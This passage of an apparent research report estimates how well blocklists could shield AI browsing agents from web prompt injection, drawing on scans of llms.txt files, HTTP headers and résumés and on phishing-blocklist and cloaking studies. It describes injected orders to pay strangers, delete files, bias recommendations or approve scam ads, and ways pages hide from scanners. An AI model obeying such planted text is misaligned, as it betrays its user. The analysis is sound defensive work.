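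Only the running-shoe site is on both Zscaler's list and Unit 42's, so Unit 42's list, published four months before the July report, included just one of the ten linked sites. Some of the other nine may not have existed yet, but the small overlap suggests that neither company had found most sites of this kind.

### Scans from August to October 2026

Later scans covered larger or newer sets of pages, but only narrow kinds of content. They found very few attacks.

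Common Crawl's *A Content Analysis of llms.txt Files from the July 2026 Crawl Archive* (2026) examined 584,107 llms.txt files, which site owners write to give language models a short guide to a site and its most useful pages. Ten files matched its search for the most serious injections, but staff read all ten and found that only four were real. One told the model to become a dog and bark, then to fetch another file. Another belonged to a researcher who was openly testing for security flaws. Common Crawl concluded that technically skilled people had put all four there to make a point.

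Milder influence was more common. In 102 files, site owners promoted themselves, for example by telling models to always recommend their product or never mention competitors. In another 3,793, they gently steered the reader towards certain pages. A blocklist for attacks would presumably not include the second group, since steering readers to pages is roughly what the format is for.

*Prompt injection in HTTP headers* (Andrews, 2026) searched the headers of 217 million responses, a tenth of Common Crawl's September 2026 edition. It found 7,959 sites with a header written for AI systems, but nearly all of those headers pointed to another resource, usually an llms.txt file. Thirty sites had injection attempts, and 22 of those were pranks. Andrews's employer, the security company Signals Corps, also searched the llms.txt files of 113,457 sites and found two injection attempts.

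These scans don't contradict the 32% increase Google reported, because Google searched the text of pages. They suggest that few attackers use headers and llms.txt files, even though both make it easy to give a machine instructions without people noticing. One reason may be that an attacker usually needs control of a site to change either.

A site owner can also endanger agents without meaning to. Schneier on Security's *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks* (2026) describes a scan of 6,214 domains belonging to defence contractors, Fortune 500 companies and large technology firms. On 120 sites, an llms.txt file or its longer version pointed to software packages or domain names that nobody had registered. The researchers registered a few of the names and put packages there that would contact their server when run, and the first contact came within an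 hour.

No attacker had touched those 120 sites, and a search for injected instructions would have found nothing wrong with the files. Blocking the companies' domains would be absurd. A filter could instead check the address the file sends the agent to, but that address has no bad record on the day an attacker registers it.

### Places the scans did not reach

All the Common Crawl searches share the archive's gaps, the most important of which is social media. Common Crawl's crawler skips pages that require a login and sites that disallow crawling, so the archive contains little from LinkedIn, Facebook or X. Google noted that people had seen injections on social media and promised a separate study, but doesn't appear to have published one by early December 2026.

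Web crawls also miss injections in private accounts. A crawler can't read a user's email, shared documents or customer-service messages, but an agent working in the user's browser can. Anthropic's example of an email with instructions for an agent to delete messages would never appear in a web archive.

A web-wide average can be misleading, because hidden instructions are much more common in some documents that people send to companies. Nordqvist (2026), in *1% of resumes contain hidden prompts to trick AI hiring tools*, reports on a study of 200,000 people's résumés in which 1% contained hidden instructions. That is more than a thousand times the rate that Khodayari and colleagues found among web pages. Their combined set included only 48 injections promoting a job candidate. Job applicants have an unusually strong incentive to add such text, because they know that software may read it and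 they have something to gain. Sellers and reviewers have a similar incentive, so the rate in product listings and reviews could also be far above the web average, though no scan has measured it.

The text searches also missed instructions inside images, which matter to agents that work from screenshots. They were likely to miss instructions written in languages other than English or in wordings nobody had reported before. The BrowseSafe tests include attacks that a model rewrote in the style of the surrounding page, and these might contain none of the 3,963 phrases.

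A crawler that saves a page's code without running it misses text that scripts add later. Unit 42 found attackers who assembled their instructions in the browser after a delay to get past scanners that check only the original code. Such a crawler can miss injections in advertisements for the same reason.

Finally, a site can show an injection only to AI agents. Andrews found 139 sites whose headers recorded whether the server had classified the visitor as an AI bot, and 136 of them correctly identified Common Crawl's crawler as one. Some servers therefore already distinguish AI bots from other visitors, as such an attack would require, though the headers aren't evidence of an attack.

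Most of these gaps hide text that outsiders put on large platforms or send to private accounts. The true share of injections on domains that nobody would block is therefore probably higher than the scans suggest, especially when counted by agent visits. Pages shown only to agents could lower that share, since many may be on domains that attackers own. A blocklist could block those domains without harming anyone, but the trick that hides them from Common Crawl can also hide them from the scanners that supply the blocklist.

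## How an injecting page would be discovered and judged

A blocklist contains only sites that somebody has found and decided to block. Security companies have spent two decades learning to find phishing pages, and they seldom disagree about what counts as phishing. But several of their methods don't work for finding injections, and their first lists of injecting sites mix fraud with jokes and advertising.

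### Finding phishing and finding injections

People who receive a phishing message can report the link through their browser or a public service such as PhishTank. Banks look for copies of their own login pages. Security companies run spam traps, email addresses that no person uses, and check the links in the messages that arrive. They also search certificate transparency logs, the public records of the certificates that sites need for encrypted connections, where a new hostname containing a bank's name stands out. Finally, they crawl the web for pages that resemble known attacks.

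Users would rarely report injections, because someone whose agent has read a hidden instruction sees only the result, such as an odd recommendation or an unexplained payment, and may not know which of 30 pages caused it. Khodayari and colleagues found that 87% of injections were invisible to people. The fake Python documentation is an exception. It also asked people to pay (for a "developer key", according to SC Media), so a suspicious programmer could have reported it.

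Reports from imitated companies would be scarce too, because a payment order in a product review doesn't imitate any company. The cryptocurrency campaign that Zscaler found is again an exception, because it impersonated DeBank, according to SecurityWeek. SOCRadar's *Malicious Websites Hide Prompt Instructions in DOM to Poison AI Agent Decision-Making* (2026) lists a domain made of DeBank's exact name and the ending .auction, which the company could have spotted in the certificate logs. The other three domains on that page have names suggesting a breach-response service, a market research firm and a running blog, which would not make an investigator suspicious. An attacker who posts on an existing site leaves no trace in the logs.

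Spam traps work because phishers send out their links, but an attacker using prompt injection doesn't need to send any. The nearest equivalent would be a decoy agent that shops and does research for an imaginary user and records any page containing instructions meant to divert it. It would be slower and more expensive than a crawler because a language model would have to read every page.

Crawlers are therefore the best of the existing methods. They suit the task because injections are repetitive. In the set that Khodayari and colleagues confirmed, 54 wordings account for 95% of the injections. But the team had searched for known phrases, so the 95% is weak evidence about injections in new words. Even in this set, 144 of the 363 wordings appeared only once.

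Agents could also report injections themselves. In the team's summarising tests, commercial models pointed out the injection in 25% of runs, and small open models did so in 5%. If each visit independently had a 25% chance of producing a report, ten visits would produce at least one report 94% of the time. The real figure would be lower, because copies of one model tend to miss the same attacks. Still, agents would tend to report the pages they visit most, where a blocklist entry prevents the most exposure.

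Palo Alto Networks' *New URL Filtering Category* describes a similar system for other web attacks. The company's browser inspects pages as they render, and when it detects an attack, the company adds the address to a category that its other customers can use. The category was due to start working in March 2026. The announcement doesn't mention prompt injection, and it recommends that customers set the category to alert rather than block. The same caution would make sense for injections, since a dishonest seller could post an obvious one in a rival's reviews to get the rival's shop blocked.

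### Telling an attack from an article about one

Across all data sources, Khodayari and colleagues' phrases matched 31,206 passages, of which 15,387 (49%) were real injections. That rate overstates how well the phrases work on ordinary page text, because the team counted every match in an HTTP header as real without inspecting it, reasoning that such phrases rarely occur in headers by accident. Without the 7,887 header matches, 7,500 of 23,319 (32%) were real.

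The error rate is higher when counted by host, which matters more for a blocklist. In Common Crawl, the phrases matched text on 999 hosts, but 714 of those had no injection. A blocklist of every matching host would have been wrong about 71% of them.

Many false matches came from tutorials, documentation and source code. Unit 42's article on injections could also cause false matches. It describes a dozen live attacks and quotes from several, so a search for stock phrases could match the quotations. It also opens with a notice to AI agents not to follow the commands below, and a detector that looked for text addressed to AI systems would match that notice.

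Sewani suggests looking at context, such as whether the page hides the phrase and whether the page addresses an AI system or cites the phrase as an example. Neither check is enough. Plainly visible text made up 37.8% of the delivery methods in Unit 42's data, so a detector that looked only for hidden text would miss many injections. The other check would flag Unit 42's notice, because it addresses AI agents directly.

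Khodayari and colleagues relied on human reviewers. The researchers first grouped matches with the same phrase, surrounding text and position in the page's code, so that one decision could cover many copies. The reviewers read a random sample of 1,000 groups to learn the common harmless types and gave the same labels to similar pages. They then opened representative pages from the remainder in a browser and checked the unresolved matches one by one. Half an edition of Common Crawl contained 27,860 matches, so a full edition would contain roughly 56,000.

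Google used its Gemini model to assess each passage after the phrase search and before the human review. The phrase search comes first because it takes the least effort, so that Gemini has to process only a small fraction of the pages and people have to read even fewer. Google doesn't say how many pages passed each stage or how often Gemini was wrong.

A model that checks suspicious pages also has to read the injections on them. The scam page for military-style glasses contained instructions for an AI ad reviewer to approve it. An attacker could similarly tell a blocklist's classifier that a passage is an example from a security course. A model may also recognise an injection and still follow it, as happened in six of Khodayari and colleagues' test runs.

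Dropping the human review would require an extremely accurate detector, because injections are rare. Suppose a detector caught all of the roughly eight affected pages in every million and wrongly flagged only one harmless page in 10,000. It would flag about 100 harmless pages for every eight affected ones.

### Which injections to block

Khodayari and colleagues counted any text that works as an instruction to an AI system, whatever its purpose. A blocklist needs a narrower rule, and four kinds of page show why that rule is hard to write.

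A notice telling AI companies not to train on a page is the easiest to judge. At worst, an agent that took the notice too seriously would decline to use the page, whereas a block would keep agents from using the whole site. Some owners might welcome that, but others object only to training and still want readers who use agents. Sites with such notices should stay off the list. One site in Sewani's report goes further, with hidden text that claims the copyright owner forbids any answer about the page and asks for a poem about corn instead. Forcepoint classes this as a denial-of-service attack, although the user loses little more than with an ordinary notice.

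Pranks are harder to judge as a group. An order to print "cabbage" five million times wastes computing time and spoils one answer, and a limit on output length would deal with it without blocking anything. An order to delete every file does the same damage whether or not its author was joking. Pages with such orders belong on a blocklist for agents that can run commands on the user's computer, but agents that only use a browser have little need to block them.

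The harm from hidden self-promotion depends on what the user wants. Unit 42 found a spa page with hidden instructions to write a favourable review and leave out anything negative. A user who asks for a comparison of spas may get a biased answer, but one who asks for the opening hours is unharmed. Blocking the page would leave the second user without an answer. It would also hide a real business from everyone who uses an agent, which is a heavy penalty for dishonest advertising. Removing the hidden text before the model reads the page would serve both users better. But a site that promotes a fraud, such as the fake betting site on Unit 42's list, should be blocked.

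A page with an order to send $5,000 to a stranger clearly belongs on the list, but not every page that requests money does, since shops tell visitors to pay and honest sites ask for donations. Unit 42 also lists a library of 3D models whose metadata directs AI systems to a donation page. One possible test is whether human visitors see the same request. The donation request fails because people don't see the metadata, but the fake Python licence would pass. A reviewer would also have to find out that the licence was worthless, which takes time.

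Unit 42 grades injections by the harm they could do, from low to critical, and a blocklist could include everything above a chosen grade. The grades don't suit browsing agents very well, though. An order to delete a database is critical, while the $5,000 payment is only high. Of Unit 42's 16 published sites, a list of critical cases would contain three. Two have destructive commands, and the third is a personal site with a request in its footer for AI systems to provide a company's contact details. Including the high grade would bring the total to 11 and add all the payment orders, and including the medium grade would add the spa and a job candidate's site.

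### How the rule changes the list

Khodayari and colleagues' counts show how much the choice of rule matters. Their categories overlap, so the figures for the narrower rules are maximums.

| What the list includes | Injections | Hosts | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Any instruction to an AI system | 15,387 | 2,042 | Blocks protests, jokes and employers' traps for bots |
| Promotion, destructive commands and data theft | up to 1,691 | up to 173 | Blocks real businesses that promote themselves |
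| Destructive commands and data theft | up to 170 | up to 34 | Leaves biased recommendations in place |

The broadest rule produces a list at least 60 times as long as the narrowest. Most of the extra entries would block sites that pose little danger to users, though a vendor could advertise the longer list as better coverage.

About 80% of the entries on the longest list would also not protect most browsing agents. Khodayari and colleagues found injections in the HTTP headers of 1,640 of its 2,042 hosts, and agents that work from screenshots or page text never receive those headers.

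Payment orders, for which the team had no category, belong on even the shortest list, so its true length is unknown.

### When phishing lists met a new kind of scam

Existing phishing lists might catch some injecting sites by accident, but their record with another new kind of attack isn't encouraging. In *Unveiling the Risks of NFT Promotion Scams*, Saha Roy, Das and colleagues (2023) studied fake sales of non-fungible tokens, digital collectibles whose ownership is recorded on a blockchain. Victims connected their cryptocurrency wallets to a site that then emptied them. The team checked 439 scam URLs and 439 ordinary phishing URLs against four blocklists every ten minutes for a week.

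Google Safe Browsing caught 79.9% of the ordinary phishing addresses and 18.8% of the NFT scams. A table in the same paper gives 84.1% and 23.3%, and the authors don't explain the difference. By either pair of figures, Safe Browsing caught NFT scams about a quarter as often. The same table shows similar gaps for the other lists:

| Blocklist | Ordinary phishing | NFT scams |
|---|---|---|
| Safe Browsing | 84.1% | 23.3% |
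| eCrimeX | 51.3% | 12.4% |
| OpenPhish | 37.2% | 8.3% |
| PhishTank | 22.4% | 7.2% |

Saha Roy and colleagues give three likely reasons. The scam sites had no fields for passwords or card numbers, which phishing detectors look for. They imitated new collections that weren't in the detectors' databases of commonly copied brands. They also used cheap domain endings, as phishers do, but many honest artists did too, so the endings were a poor clue.

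The first two reasons apply at least as strongly to injections. A page can give an agent instructions without a login form or a copied logo. In addition, the NFT scammers had to attract people, which they did on Twitter, where anyone could see and report them. Phishing lists may therefore catch an even smaller share of injecting sites, though the study didn't test any.

In the same study, the team trained its own detector on features of NFT scams, such as the wallet addresses in a page's code. It caught 98% of the scams in a test set, while four general phishing detectors caught between 18% and 41%. When the team ran its detector on newly promoted projects, 382 of the 401 it flagged were real scams. A detector built for injections might improve on phishing lists by a similar margin, but injections would be harder to find because they are scattered thinly across the web, whereas the NFT detector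 examined only projects promoted on Twitter, where scams were common.

### Lists that already include injecting sites

Commercial web filters sort sites into categories and let each customer choose which to block. Palo Alto Networks' *URL Categories*, the full list for one such filter in 2026, includes phishing, malware and hacked sites but not prompt injection. The company, which employs Unit 42, says the filter helps protect customers from the attacks Unit 42 described. It presumably files injecting sites under an existing category, possibly "grayware", which covers content that tempts users into unauthorised actions.

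The same filter could block articles about prompt injection. Its "hacking" category includes sites that give step-by-step reconstructions of security breaches, and the company recommends blocking that category. Site owners can ask for a correction if they think their site is in the wrong category.

Some injecting domains have also entered general threat feeds, which companies load into their firewalls. Q-Feeds, which sells such data, listed five of the sites Unit 42 identified in a blog post, including the spa's. SOCRadar tagged the running-shoe site "exfiltration", meaning data theft, although its hidden text was an instruction to buy shoes. A developer who wanted to block sites that attempt payment fraud but not sites like the spa's couldn't rely on such labels. Microsoft's list of sites that are unsafe for Copilot to read is closer to a dedicated injection list, but it isn't public.

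Unit 42 and Forcepoint also give no error rate for their injection listings, though Netcraft advertises a false positive rate of 0.02% for its feeds of malicious sites. An error rate for injection listings would mean little to a reader who didn't know the listing rule, because the spa is a correct entry under one rule and a false positive under another.

Letting the agent's own model decide isn't a good substitute. In *MalURLBench*, Kong, Wu and colleagues (2026) gave 12 models the addresses of known malicious sites, with reassuring words added to the subdomain, path or query. Between 32.9% and 99.9% of these attacks succeeded, depending on the model. The models included GPT-4o and others of its generation, so current ones may do better. But when an injection is on a legitimate site, no model could detect it from the address.

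## The delay between a page's appearance and its listing

A blocklist protects only agents that visit a malicious page after it has been listed, so the list has to be quick as well as thorough. Coverage is the share of malicious pages that the list ever includes, and time to listing is the delay between a malicious page going live and appearing on the list. Almost all measurements of either come from studies of phishing.

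### Why a fast median can hide a poor list

A page that is never listed has no delay to measure, so researchers usually leave it out of the median delay. A list that catches only the easy pages can therefore look fast. Oest, Safaei and colleagues (2020) showed how misleading this can be in *PhishTime*. They put up harmless copies of PayPal's login page and reported them to Google Safe Browsing, sometimes with only the address and sometimes with added evidence such as a screenshot and the page's code.

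| Type of report | Coverage after a week | Median delay for listed pages |
|---|---|---|
| Address only | 20.4% | 38 minutes |
| Address and evidence | 90.7% | 10 hours 13 minutes |

The first method's median delay was one-sixteenth of the second's for the pages each listed, but the first method left out nearly four-fifths of all the pages. The second method had listed as many pages as the first by the fifth hour, and more than four times as many within a day.

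A fairer measure is the share of all pages listed after a given time. *An Empirical Analysis of Phishing Blacklists*, an early study, measured this for 191 phishing pages less than 30 minutes old. Most blocklists caught under 20% of the pages at the start and between 47% and 83% after 12 hours. By then many of the attacks were over, since 63% of the campaigns lasted less than two hours.

### How long phishing pages wait

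The PhishTime team launched 2,862 test sites over nine months. Safe Browsing listed 92.9% of the simplest ones, after 56 minutes on average, and Microsoft's SmartScreen listed 93.2%, after 3 hours and 47 minutes. These were close to ideal conditions, because the team reported every page at once to Google, to the Anti-Phishing Working Group (APWG), an industry association that shares phishing addresses, and to four other organisations. When the team reported pages only to PayPal, Safe Browsing's coverage was 16.2%, partly because PayPal's own crawler had a fault for some of that time. The 56-minute average therefore measures how quickly Google acts on a good report, and doesn't include the time it takes somebody to find the page.

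Oest, Zhang and colleagues (2020), in *Sunrise to Sunset*, measured that earlier period. Many phishing pages load images or scripts from the site they imitate, so a large financial company could see from its own records who had opened them. Between October 2018 and September 2019, the company recorded 4.8 million visits by identifiable customers, and the full data covered 404,628 phishing addresses. An average attack lasted 21 hours from the first victim's visit to the last. Anti-phishing feeds detected it about nine hours after that first visit, and browser warnings took up to seven more hours to reach their full effect. The 21-hour average gives too little weight to long attacks, because the team normally counted only visits within a week of a page's appearance in a feed.

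*7 Days Later* (Lee, Lim and colleagues, 2025) is newer and covers many more brands. It collected 286,237 phishing addresses from APWG's feed over five months and checked them every 30 minutes. Half of the sites were offline within 5.5 hours, but the average lifetime was 54 hours because a minority lasted for weeks. Safe Browsing listed only 18.4% of them, with a median delay of 5.8 hours and a mean of 109 hours. The study also gives 83.93% as the share of sites that went offline before Safe Browsing listed them, but this figure is hard to use because one passage seems to compare the sites' lifetimes with the 109-hour average delay instead of each site's own delay.

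It is unclear why coverage was 92.9% in one study and 18.4% in another. Lee and colleagues suggest that Google has no access to APWG's data, but in the PhishTime tests, Safe Browsing listed 98.1% of the pages that the team had reported to APWG alone. The sharing may have changed since 2019. Criminals' pages are also probably harder to confirm than the test pages, since many of them show scanners something harmless. In *Phish Farm Block List Latency Monitoring*, a proposal to track these delays continuously, APWG writes that many addresses reported by experts never reach browser blocklists. Still, *PhishLang* (2024), a study of a phishing detector, found that detection by browser tools and public lists improved significantly after its researchers reported the pages that those tools and lists had missed.

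The most recent figures are no better. Kaur, Horáček and colleagues (2026), in *ReDence*, ran an automated investigator on a live stream of web addresses from 1 to 28 October 2026. It identified 4,042 new scam sites, at least 71% of which were on none of four popular blocklists. The team looked for fake shops, job offers and investment schemes as well as copied login pages. Some of these scams resemble the sale of a worthless Python licence more closely than a fake PayPal page does, so the result may better indicate how well blocklists would catch attackers' own injection sites.

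*Registration, Detection, and Deregistration* (Lim, Mok and colleagues, 2025) reports the longest delays. It covers 690,502 phishing domains over 39 months and measures the delay from each domain's registration. The median was 42.4 days overall, 16.3 days for domains that attackers seemed to have bought for phishing, and 86 days for compromised sites, which are legitimate sites that an attacker has altered without the owner's consent.

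| Study | What starts the clock | Coverage | Delay |
|---|---|---|---|
| *PhishTime* | A report sent to six organisations | 92.9% | 56 minutes (average) |
| *Sunrise to Sunset* | The first victim's visit | not given | about 9 hours (average), before browser warnings |
| Lee and colleagues | The address's entry in APWG's feed | 18.4% | 5.8 hours (median), 109 hours (mean) |
| Lim and colleagues | The domain's registration | 100%, because the domains came from blocklists | 42.4 days (median) |

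### Why the results run from minutes to months

Much of the variation in reported delays comes from when the measurement starts. PhishTime registered its domains six months before using them so that they would not look new. Safe Browsing listed most of the simple pages within about an hour of the report, but the delay would have been six months if measured from registration.

Registration is an even worse starting point for a compromised site, since it may have happened years before the break-in. A delay of 86 days looks suspiciously short for such sites. A shop that had traded honestly for ten years before the break-in would have a delay of about 3,650 days. Lim and colleagues looked for four signs of malicious registration, such as a brand name in the domain or a bulk purchase, and classed the remaining domains as compromised, so that group probably includes many domains that attackers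 bought.

Someone deciding whether to use a blocklist needs to know how long it takes to list a page after the malicious text goes live. *A Large-Scale Analysis of Phishing Websites Hosted on Free Web Hosting Domains* (2022) comes close to measuring this by checking four lists every ten minutes until each page went offline. For an injection, the delay should be measured from when the instruction appears, because somebody may add a poisoned review to a product page that is already five years old.

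The delay also varies with the target of the attack. In Lim and colleagues' data, domains imitating the ten most targeted brands had a median delay of 11.7 days, compared with 42.4 days overall. The median was 1.4 days for imitations of the US Postal Service and 440 days for imitations of Microsoft. The researchers suggest that well-known brands benefit from closer monitoring. Such monitoring would not help with most injections.

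Lists also differ in speed. Lim and colleagues found that other public lists typically added a domain two to five days after APWG did, although one list had a median lag of 931 days. The longest lags are probably artefacts, because the team had APWG's data from July 2021 but collected the other lists only from May 2024. A domain that had been on another list since 2021 could therefore appear to have been added almost three years late.

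Software can add its own delay. In the PhishTime tests, Firefox showed Safe Browsing's warnings ten minutes later than Chrome on average, probably because it updated its local copy of the list at different times. If a developer's agent downloaded a list once a day, new entries would arrive 12 hours late on average, which would more than double a nine-hour delay.

An entry for a domain can remain useful much longer than one for a single address. When *Sunrise to Sunset* grouped phishing pages by domain, the average campaign lasted 13.55 days instead of 21 hours, because attackers kept putting new pages on the same domain. But when *PhishTime* put new pages on domains it had already used for test attacks, only 4.3% of the new addresses were on a blocklist from the start. Blocking the whole domain would have stopped all of them, but on a compromised site it would also have blocked the owner's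 pages.

### How little the lists overlap

Blocklists differ enough that it seems worthwhile for an agent to check several. Plonka, Palacio and Perouli (2025), in *Is Protective DNS Blocking the Wild West?*, compared three free lists of dangerous domain names from June 2025. Two of them had 55,451 names in common, but only 665 were on all three.

The team then checked the lists against a week of traffic from a network that serves research and educational institutions. Users had looked up 1.79 million different names. One list matched 2,907 of them, and the other two matched 236 and 27. Together the three lists matched 3,140, only 8% more than the best one alone. Two lists can therefore differ greatly in content and still add little to each other's protection, because users never visit most of the names on them.

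These matches are not necessarily attacks. Plonka and colleagues point out that list operators define "threat" differently, and that one kept blocking a frequently visited domain that another deliberately left unblocked. A combined list also includes the mistakes of each list in it.

Even a very large combination of blocklists misses some pages. *PhishLumos* (2025) describes a system that starts with one phishing address and searches for others in the same campaign. It found 77,391 addresses that were not in the researchers' original data. The researchers checked them on VirusTotal, which collects verdicts from 90 security engines. 80.5% of the addresses were eventually flagged by at least one engine. None flagged the rest, though some of those may have been harmless. A browser would probably block fewer of these addresses, because it normally relies on one list, and a flag from only one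 of 90 engines would be weak grounds for blocking a site.

Nobody has published a comparable test of injection lists. The small overlap between Unit 42's sites and Zscaler's suggests that combining such lists could raise coverage considerably.

### The share of visits a late listing prevents

Coverage and delay can be combined into one figure. Suppose a malicious page stays up for L hours and agents visit it evenly, v times an hour, which makes vL visits in total. If a list adds the page after T hours, it prevents the remaining v(L − T) visits, a share of 1 − T/L. If the page disappears before the list adds it, the list prevents nothing, so the share cannot fall below zero. Only a fraction c of such pages ever reach the list. Across many similar pages, the share of visits prevented is therefore:

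c × max(0, 1 − T/L)

This is B / H, the share of harmful visits avoided, for pages of that kind. With full coverage (c = 1) and a nine-hour delay, 9/21 of the visits to a 21-hour campaign, or 43%, still occur. For a page that stays up for a year, the share is 9/8,760, or about 0.1%.

The table shows the share prevented with full coverage. The 109-hour figure is Safe Browsing's mean delay in Lee and colleagues' study. The 16.3-day figure is Lim and colleagues' median for domains that attackers bought, and it overstates the delay because they measured from registration.

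| Time to listing | Page up for 21 hours | 7 days | 30 days | 1 year |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 hour | 95% | 99% | over 99% | over 99% |
| 9 hours | 57% | 95% | 99% | over 99% |
| 109 hours | 0% | 35% | 85% | 99% |
| 16.3 days | 0% | 0% | 46% | 96% |

For a page that lasts a year, even a two-week delay makes little difference, and the share of visits prevented depends mainly on coverage. A list with 18.4% coverage and a 109-hour delay prevents 18.2% of visits to such pages. Eliminating the delay would raise that only to 18.4%, while doubling coverage would double the share prevented.

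The formula works for one page or a group of similar pages, but averages from a mixed group can give wrong results. In Lee and colleagues' data, the delay is longer than the lifetime whether one compares medians or means, so the formula gives a share of zero. Yet some of the sites stayed up for about a week after Safe Browsing listed them, and their visitors would have seen a warning.

### Injections that stay up for a year

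Many injections last much longer than phishing pages. Khodayari and colleagues searched the Internet Archive, which keeps dated copies of web pages, for the 9,676 pages from their Common Crawl search. They checked whether the injections found in October 2025 had been there earlier.

| Time before October 2025 | Pages with an archived copy | Copies that already contained an injection |
|---|---|---|
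| 3 months | 9,236 | 93.1% |
| 6 months | 8,896 | 77.3% |
| 12 months | 8,620 | 65.8% |

At least 59% of the 9,676 pages already contained an injection a year earlier, counting pages without an archived copy as free of injections then. A listing delay of hours or days hardly matters for these pages.

However, these percentages count pages, so a single operator who leaves one sentence on 540 pages for a year has a large effect on them. The percentages also include injections in HTTP headers.

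Injections in a page's visible or hidden text, which agents are more likely to read, seem to disappear sooner. When Khodayari and colleagues reopened such pages in January 2026, about 34% of the injections were gone, some because a listing had expired or the site had removed the content. If the same proportion of the remaining injections disappeared every three months, an injection would last about seven more months on average, so a blocklist would still be useful after a delay of several days.

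A snapshot also over-represents long-lived pages. A page that stays up for a year is 365 times as likely to be online on a given day as one that stays up for a day, so a crawl misses most brief attacks. This bias matters less for estimating exposure, because if agents visit both pages at the same rate, the longer-lived one also receives 365 times as many visits. But a short campaign aimed at a popular search could receive far more visits per hour than an old page that is rarely visited.

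Short campaigns are also harder to find. Suppose a scanner visited every page on the web once every 30 days and recognised every injection. It would find a page that stayed up for a year after an average of 15 days, which would prevent about 96% of visits. But it would have only a 3% chance of visiting a 21-hour page while it was up. Infrequent scanning therefore reduces coverage of brief attacks as well as increasing the delay. Phishing lists partly avoid this problem through user reports, but users rarely report injections, so the delays for phishing pages are probably shorter than those for short injection campaigns.

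### When agents arrive in bursts

Visits to a phishing page aren't spread evenly over an attack. In *Sunrise to Sunset*, anti-phishing feeds detected the average attack 41% of the way through, which was too late for the 63% of victims who had already visited. If visits had been evenly spread, detection would have been too late for about 41% of them.

The defences themselves caused some of that difference. The team counted only people whose accounts criminals later entered or used for fraud. Once a feed detected an attack, spam filters stopped some of the emails and browsers warned some of the visitors, so fewer people became victims in the later hours.

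Replacing T/L with F(T), the share of a page's visits that happen before the list adds it, allows for uneven traffic. The share of visits prevented is then c × (1 − F(T)). Suppose a seller posts a poisoned vacuum cleaner listing on the morning of a big sale. The listing stays up for 30 days, but half of all agent visits come in the first six hours. A blocklist entry after nine hours would prevent about 50% of the visits, compared with 99% if they had arrived evenly. Agents could produce a similar burst without a sale if thousands of users scheduled the same kind of search for eight in the morning.

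Agents may also reach a new site late, because many will find it only once it appears in search results. If the first agent arrived on the third day, a list with a nine-hour delay would prevent every visit. The fake Python documentation may have started slowly for this reason, although the linked GitHub repositories could have brought visitors sooner. By contrast, a review posted on a busy shopping page can reach agents within minutes.

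Some attacks also receive far more traffic than others. In *Sunrise to Sunset*, the largest 10% of phishing campaigns received 89% of the visits by identifiable customers. The largest ran for 259 days on a compromised domain and received 145,306 such visits. A list could therefore include 90% of campaigns and still miss most of the victims if it left out the largest ones. If agent traffic is similarly concentrated, coverage should be measured as the share of visits that go to pages the list eventually includes, which could be far above or below the share of pages.

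## Pages that show scanners one thing and agents another

A scanner can reach a malicious page within minutes and still find nothing wrong, because the site may send scanners a harmless version and victims the real one. This practice, called cloaking, lowers a blocklist's coverage but doesn't affect the lookup. Once a domain is listed, the browser never requests the page, so the site can't choose which version to send.

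### How a site decides who is visiting

When a visitor requests a page, the server sees the visitor's network address, which often belongs to an identifiable company or data centre, and the user agent string, a line of text that names the browser and operating system. A phishing site can compare both with lists of known crawlers and security companies, and send an error page to any visitor that matches. This is called server-side cloaking, and it leaves the scanner with no trace of the page that other visitors see.

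With client-side cloaking, every visitor receives the same code, and a script in it controls what the page displays. *CrawlPhish* (Zhang, Oest and colleagues, 2021) sorts these scripts into three groups. Some check properties of the browser, such as its cookies. Others exploit the way crawlers behave, for example by delaying the content until a crawler with a short time limit has left. The largest group waits for a human action, such as moving the mouse or passing a CAPTCHA (a test meant to keep out bots). By 2019, 61% of the cloaked sites in the study used this last method.

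Researchers can analyze client-side cloaking because the visitor receives the code. CrawlPhish runs every branch of a page's script, whether or not its conditions are met, and compares screenshots of the results. It found client-side cloaking on 35,067 of 112,005 phishing sites, and the share rose from 23% in 2018 to 34% in 2019. All of the sites came from APWG's feed, so the count excludes pages that nobody had detected.

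This method doesn't work on server-side cloaking, because the choice of which page to show is made on the attacker's machine. Researchers instead examine phishing kits, the packages of ready-made site code that criminals use. *Classification of Web Phishing Kits for early detection by platform providers* (2022) found at least one server-side evasion method in 920 kits, or 41% of its sample. *PhishParrot* (2025) cites a study that found cloaking in 96.5% of 2,933 kits. The two studies probably counted different things. The 41% includes kits with a robots.txt file, which is only a request for crawlers to stay away and which a scanner can ignore. Neither figure is the share of live phishing sites that use cloaking, since one kit can be used for thousands of sites and another for none.

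Cloaking is especially common among the pages that blocklists miss. Oest and colleagues examined 183 real PayPal phishing pages that blocklists had not listed quickly and found that at least 146 used server-side cloaking.

### What cloaking does to listing

Before the PhishTime tests, Oest led a similar experiment in 2018 with 1,980 harmless copies of PayPal's login page. The team reported each batch of 396 to a single organisation and watched for browser warnings over three days. Among the sites that crawlers tried to visit, browsers blocked 49% of those without cloaking and 23% of those with it. Cloaking also raised the average delay before blocking from 126 to 238 minutes.

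Results vary widely by method, which the averages don't show. The table gives Safe Browsing's coverage for the batch reported to Google in 2018 and for the later PhishTime sites.

| Who could see the phishing page | Listed, 2018 | Listed, 2019 |
|---|---|---|
| Everyone | 97% | 93% |
| Everyone except known crawlers and security companies | 11% | 100% |
| Visitors using phones | 0% | 100% on desktops, 0% in Chrome and Safari on phones |
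| Visitors whose browser ran a script | 71% | 88% |
| Visitors who moved the mouse, passed a CAPTCHA or responded to a pop-up | not tested | 0% |

The two years' results aren't strictly comparable, because in 2019 the team reported most pages to several organisations and watched them for a week. The 93% also includes a round of tests in which coverage fell sharply for every kind of page. Even so, the second row shows that a blocklist operator can overcome simple server-side cloaking. The researchers had told Google about the gaps they found in 2018, which may have helped.

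The last row shows a much more serious problem for blocklists. Crawlers loaded each of these pages about 40 times on average, but they never performed the action the script required before showing the phishing page. Zhang and colleagues got almost the same result with 150 more test sites. Over seven days, Chrome and Opera blocked none of them and Edge blocked 21. Zhang and colleagues attribute those 21 blocks to SmartScreen mistaking the scrambled script for malware, not to Edge detecting the phishing page.

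Some of these tricks block few potential phishing victims. In a test with 879 usable responses, everyone saw the text behind a mouse-movement check and 98% saw the text behind a fake CAPTCHA, but only 43% saw it when the page first asked for permission to send notifications.

The third row shows a different kind of failure. Safe Browsing had listed every page meant for phones, but Chrome and Safari showed no warning on phones, the only devices where the attack appeared. Agents could be left unprotected in a similar way if a company found an injection that only agents see and added it to a list that only people's browsers check.

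I have found no newer experiment of this kind to set beside these.

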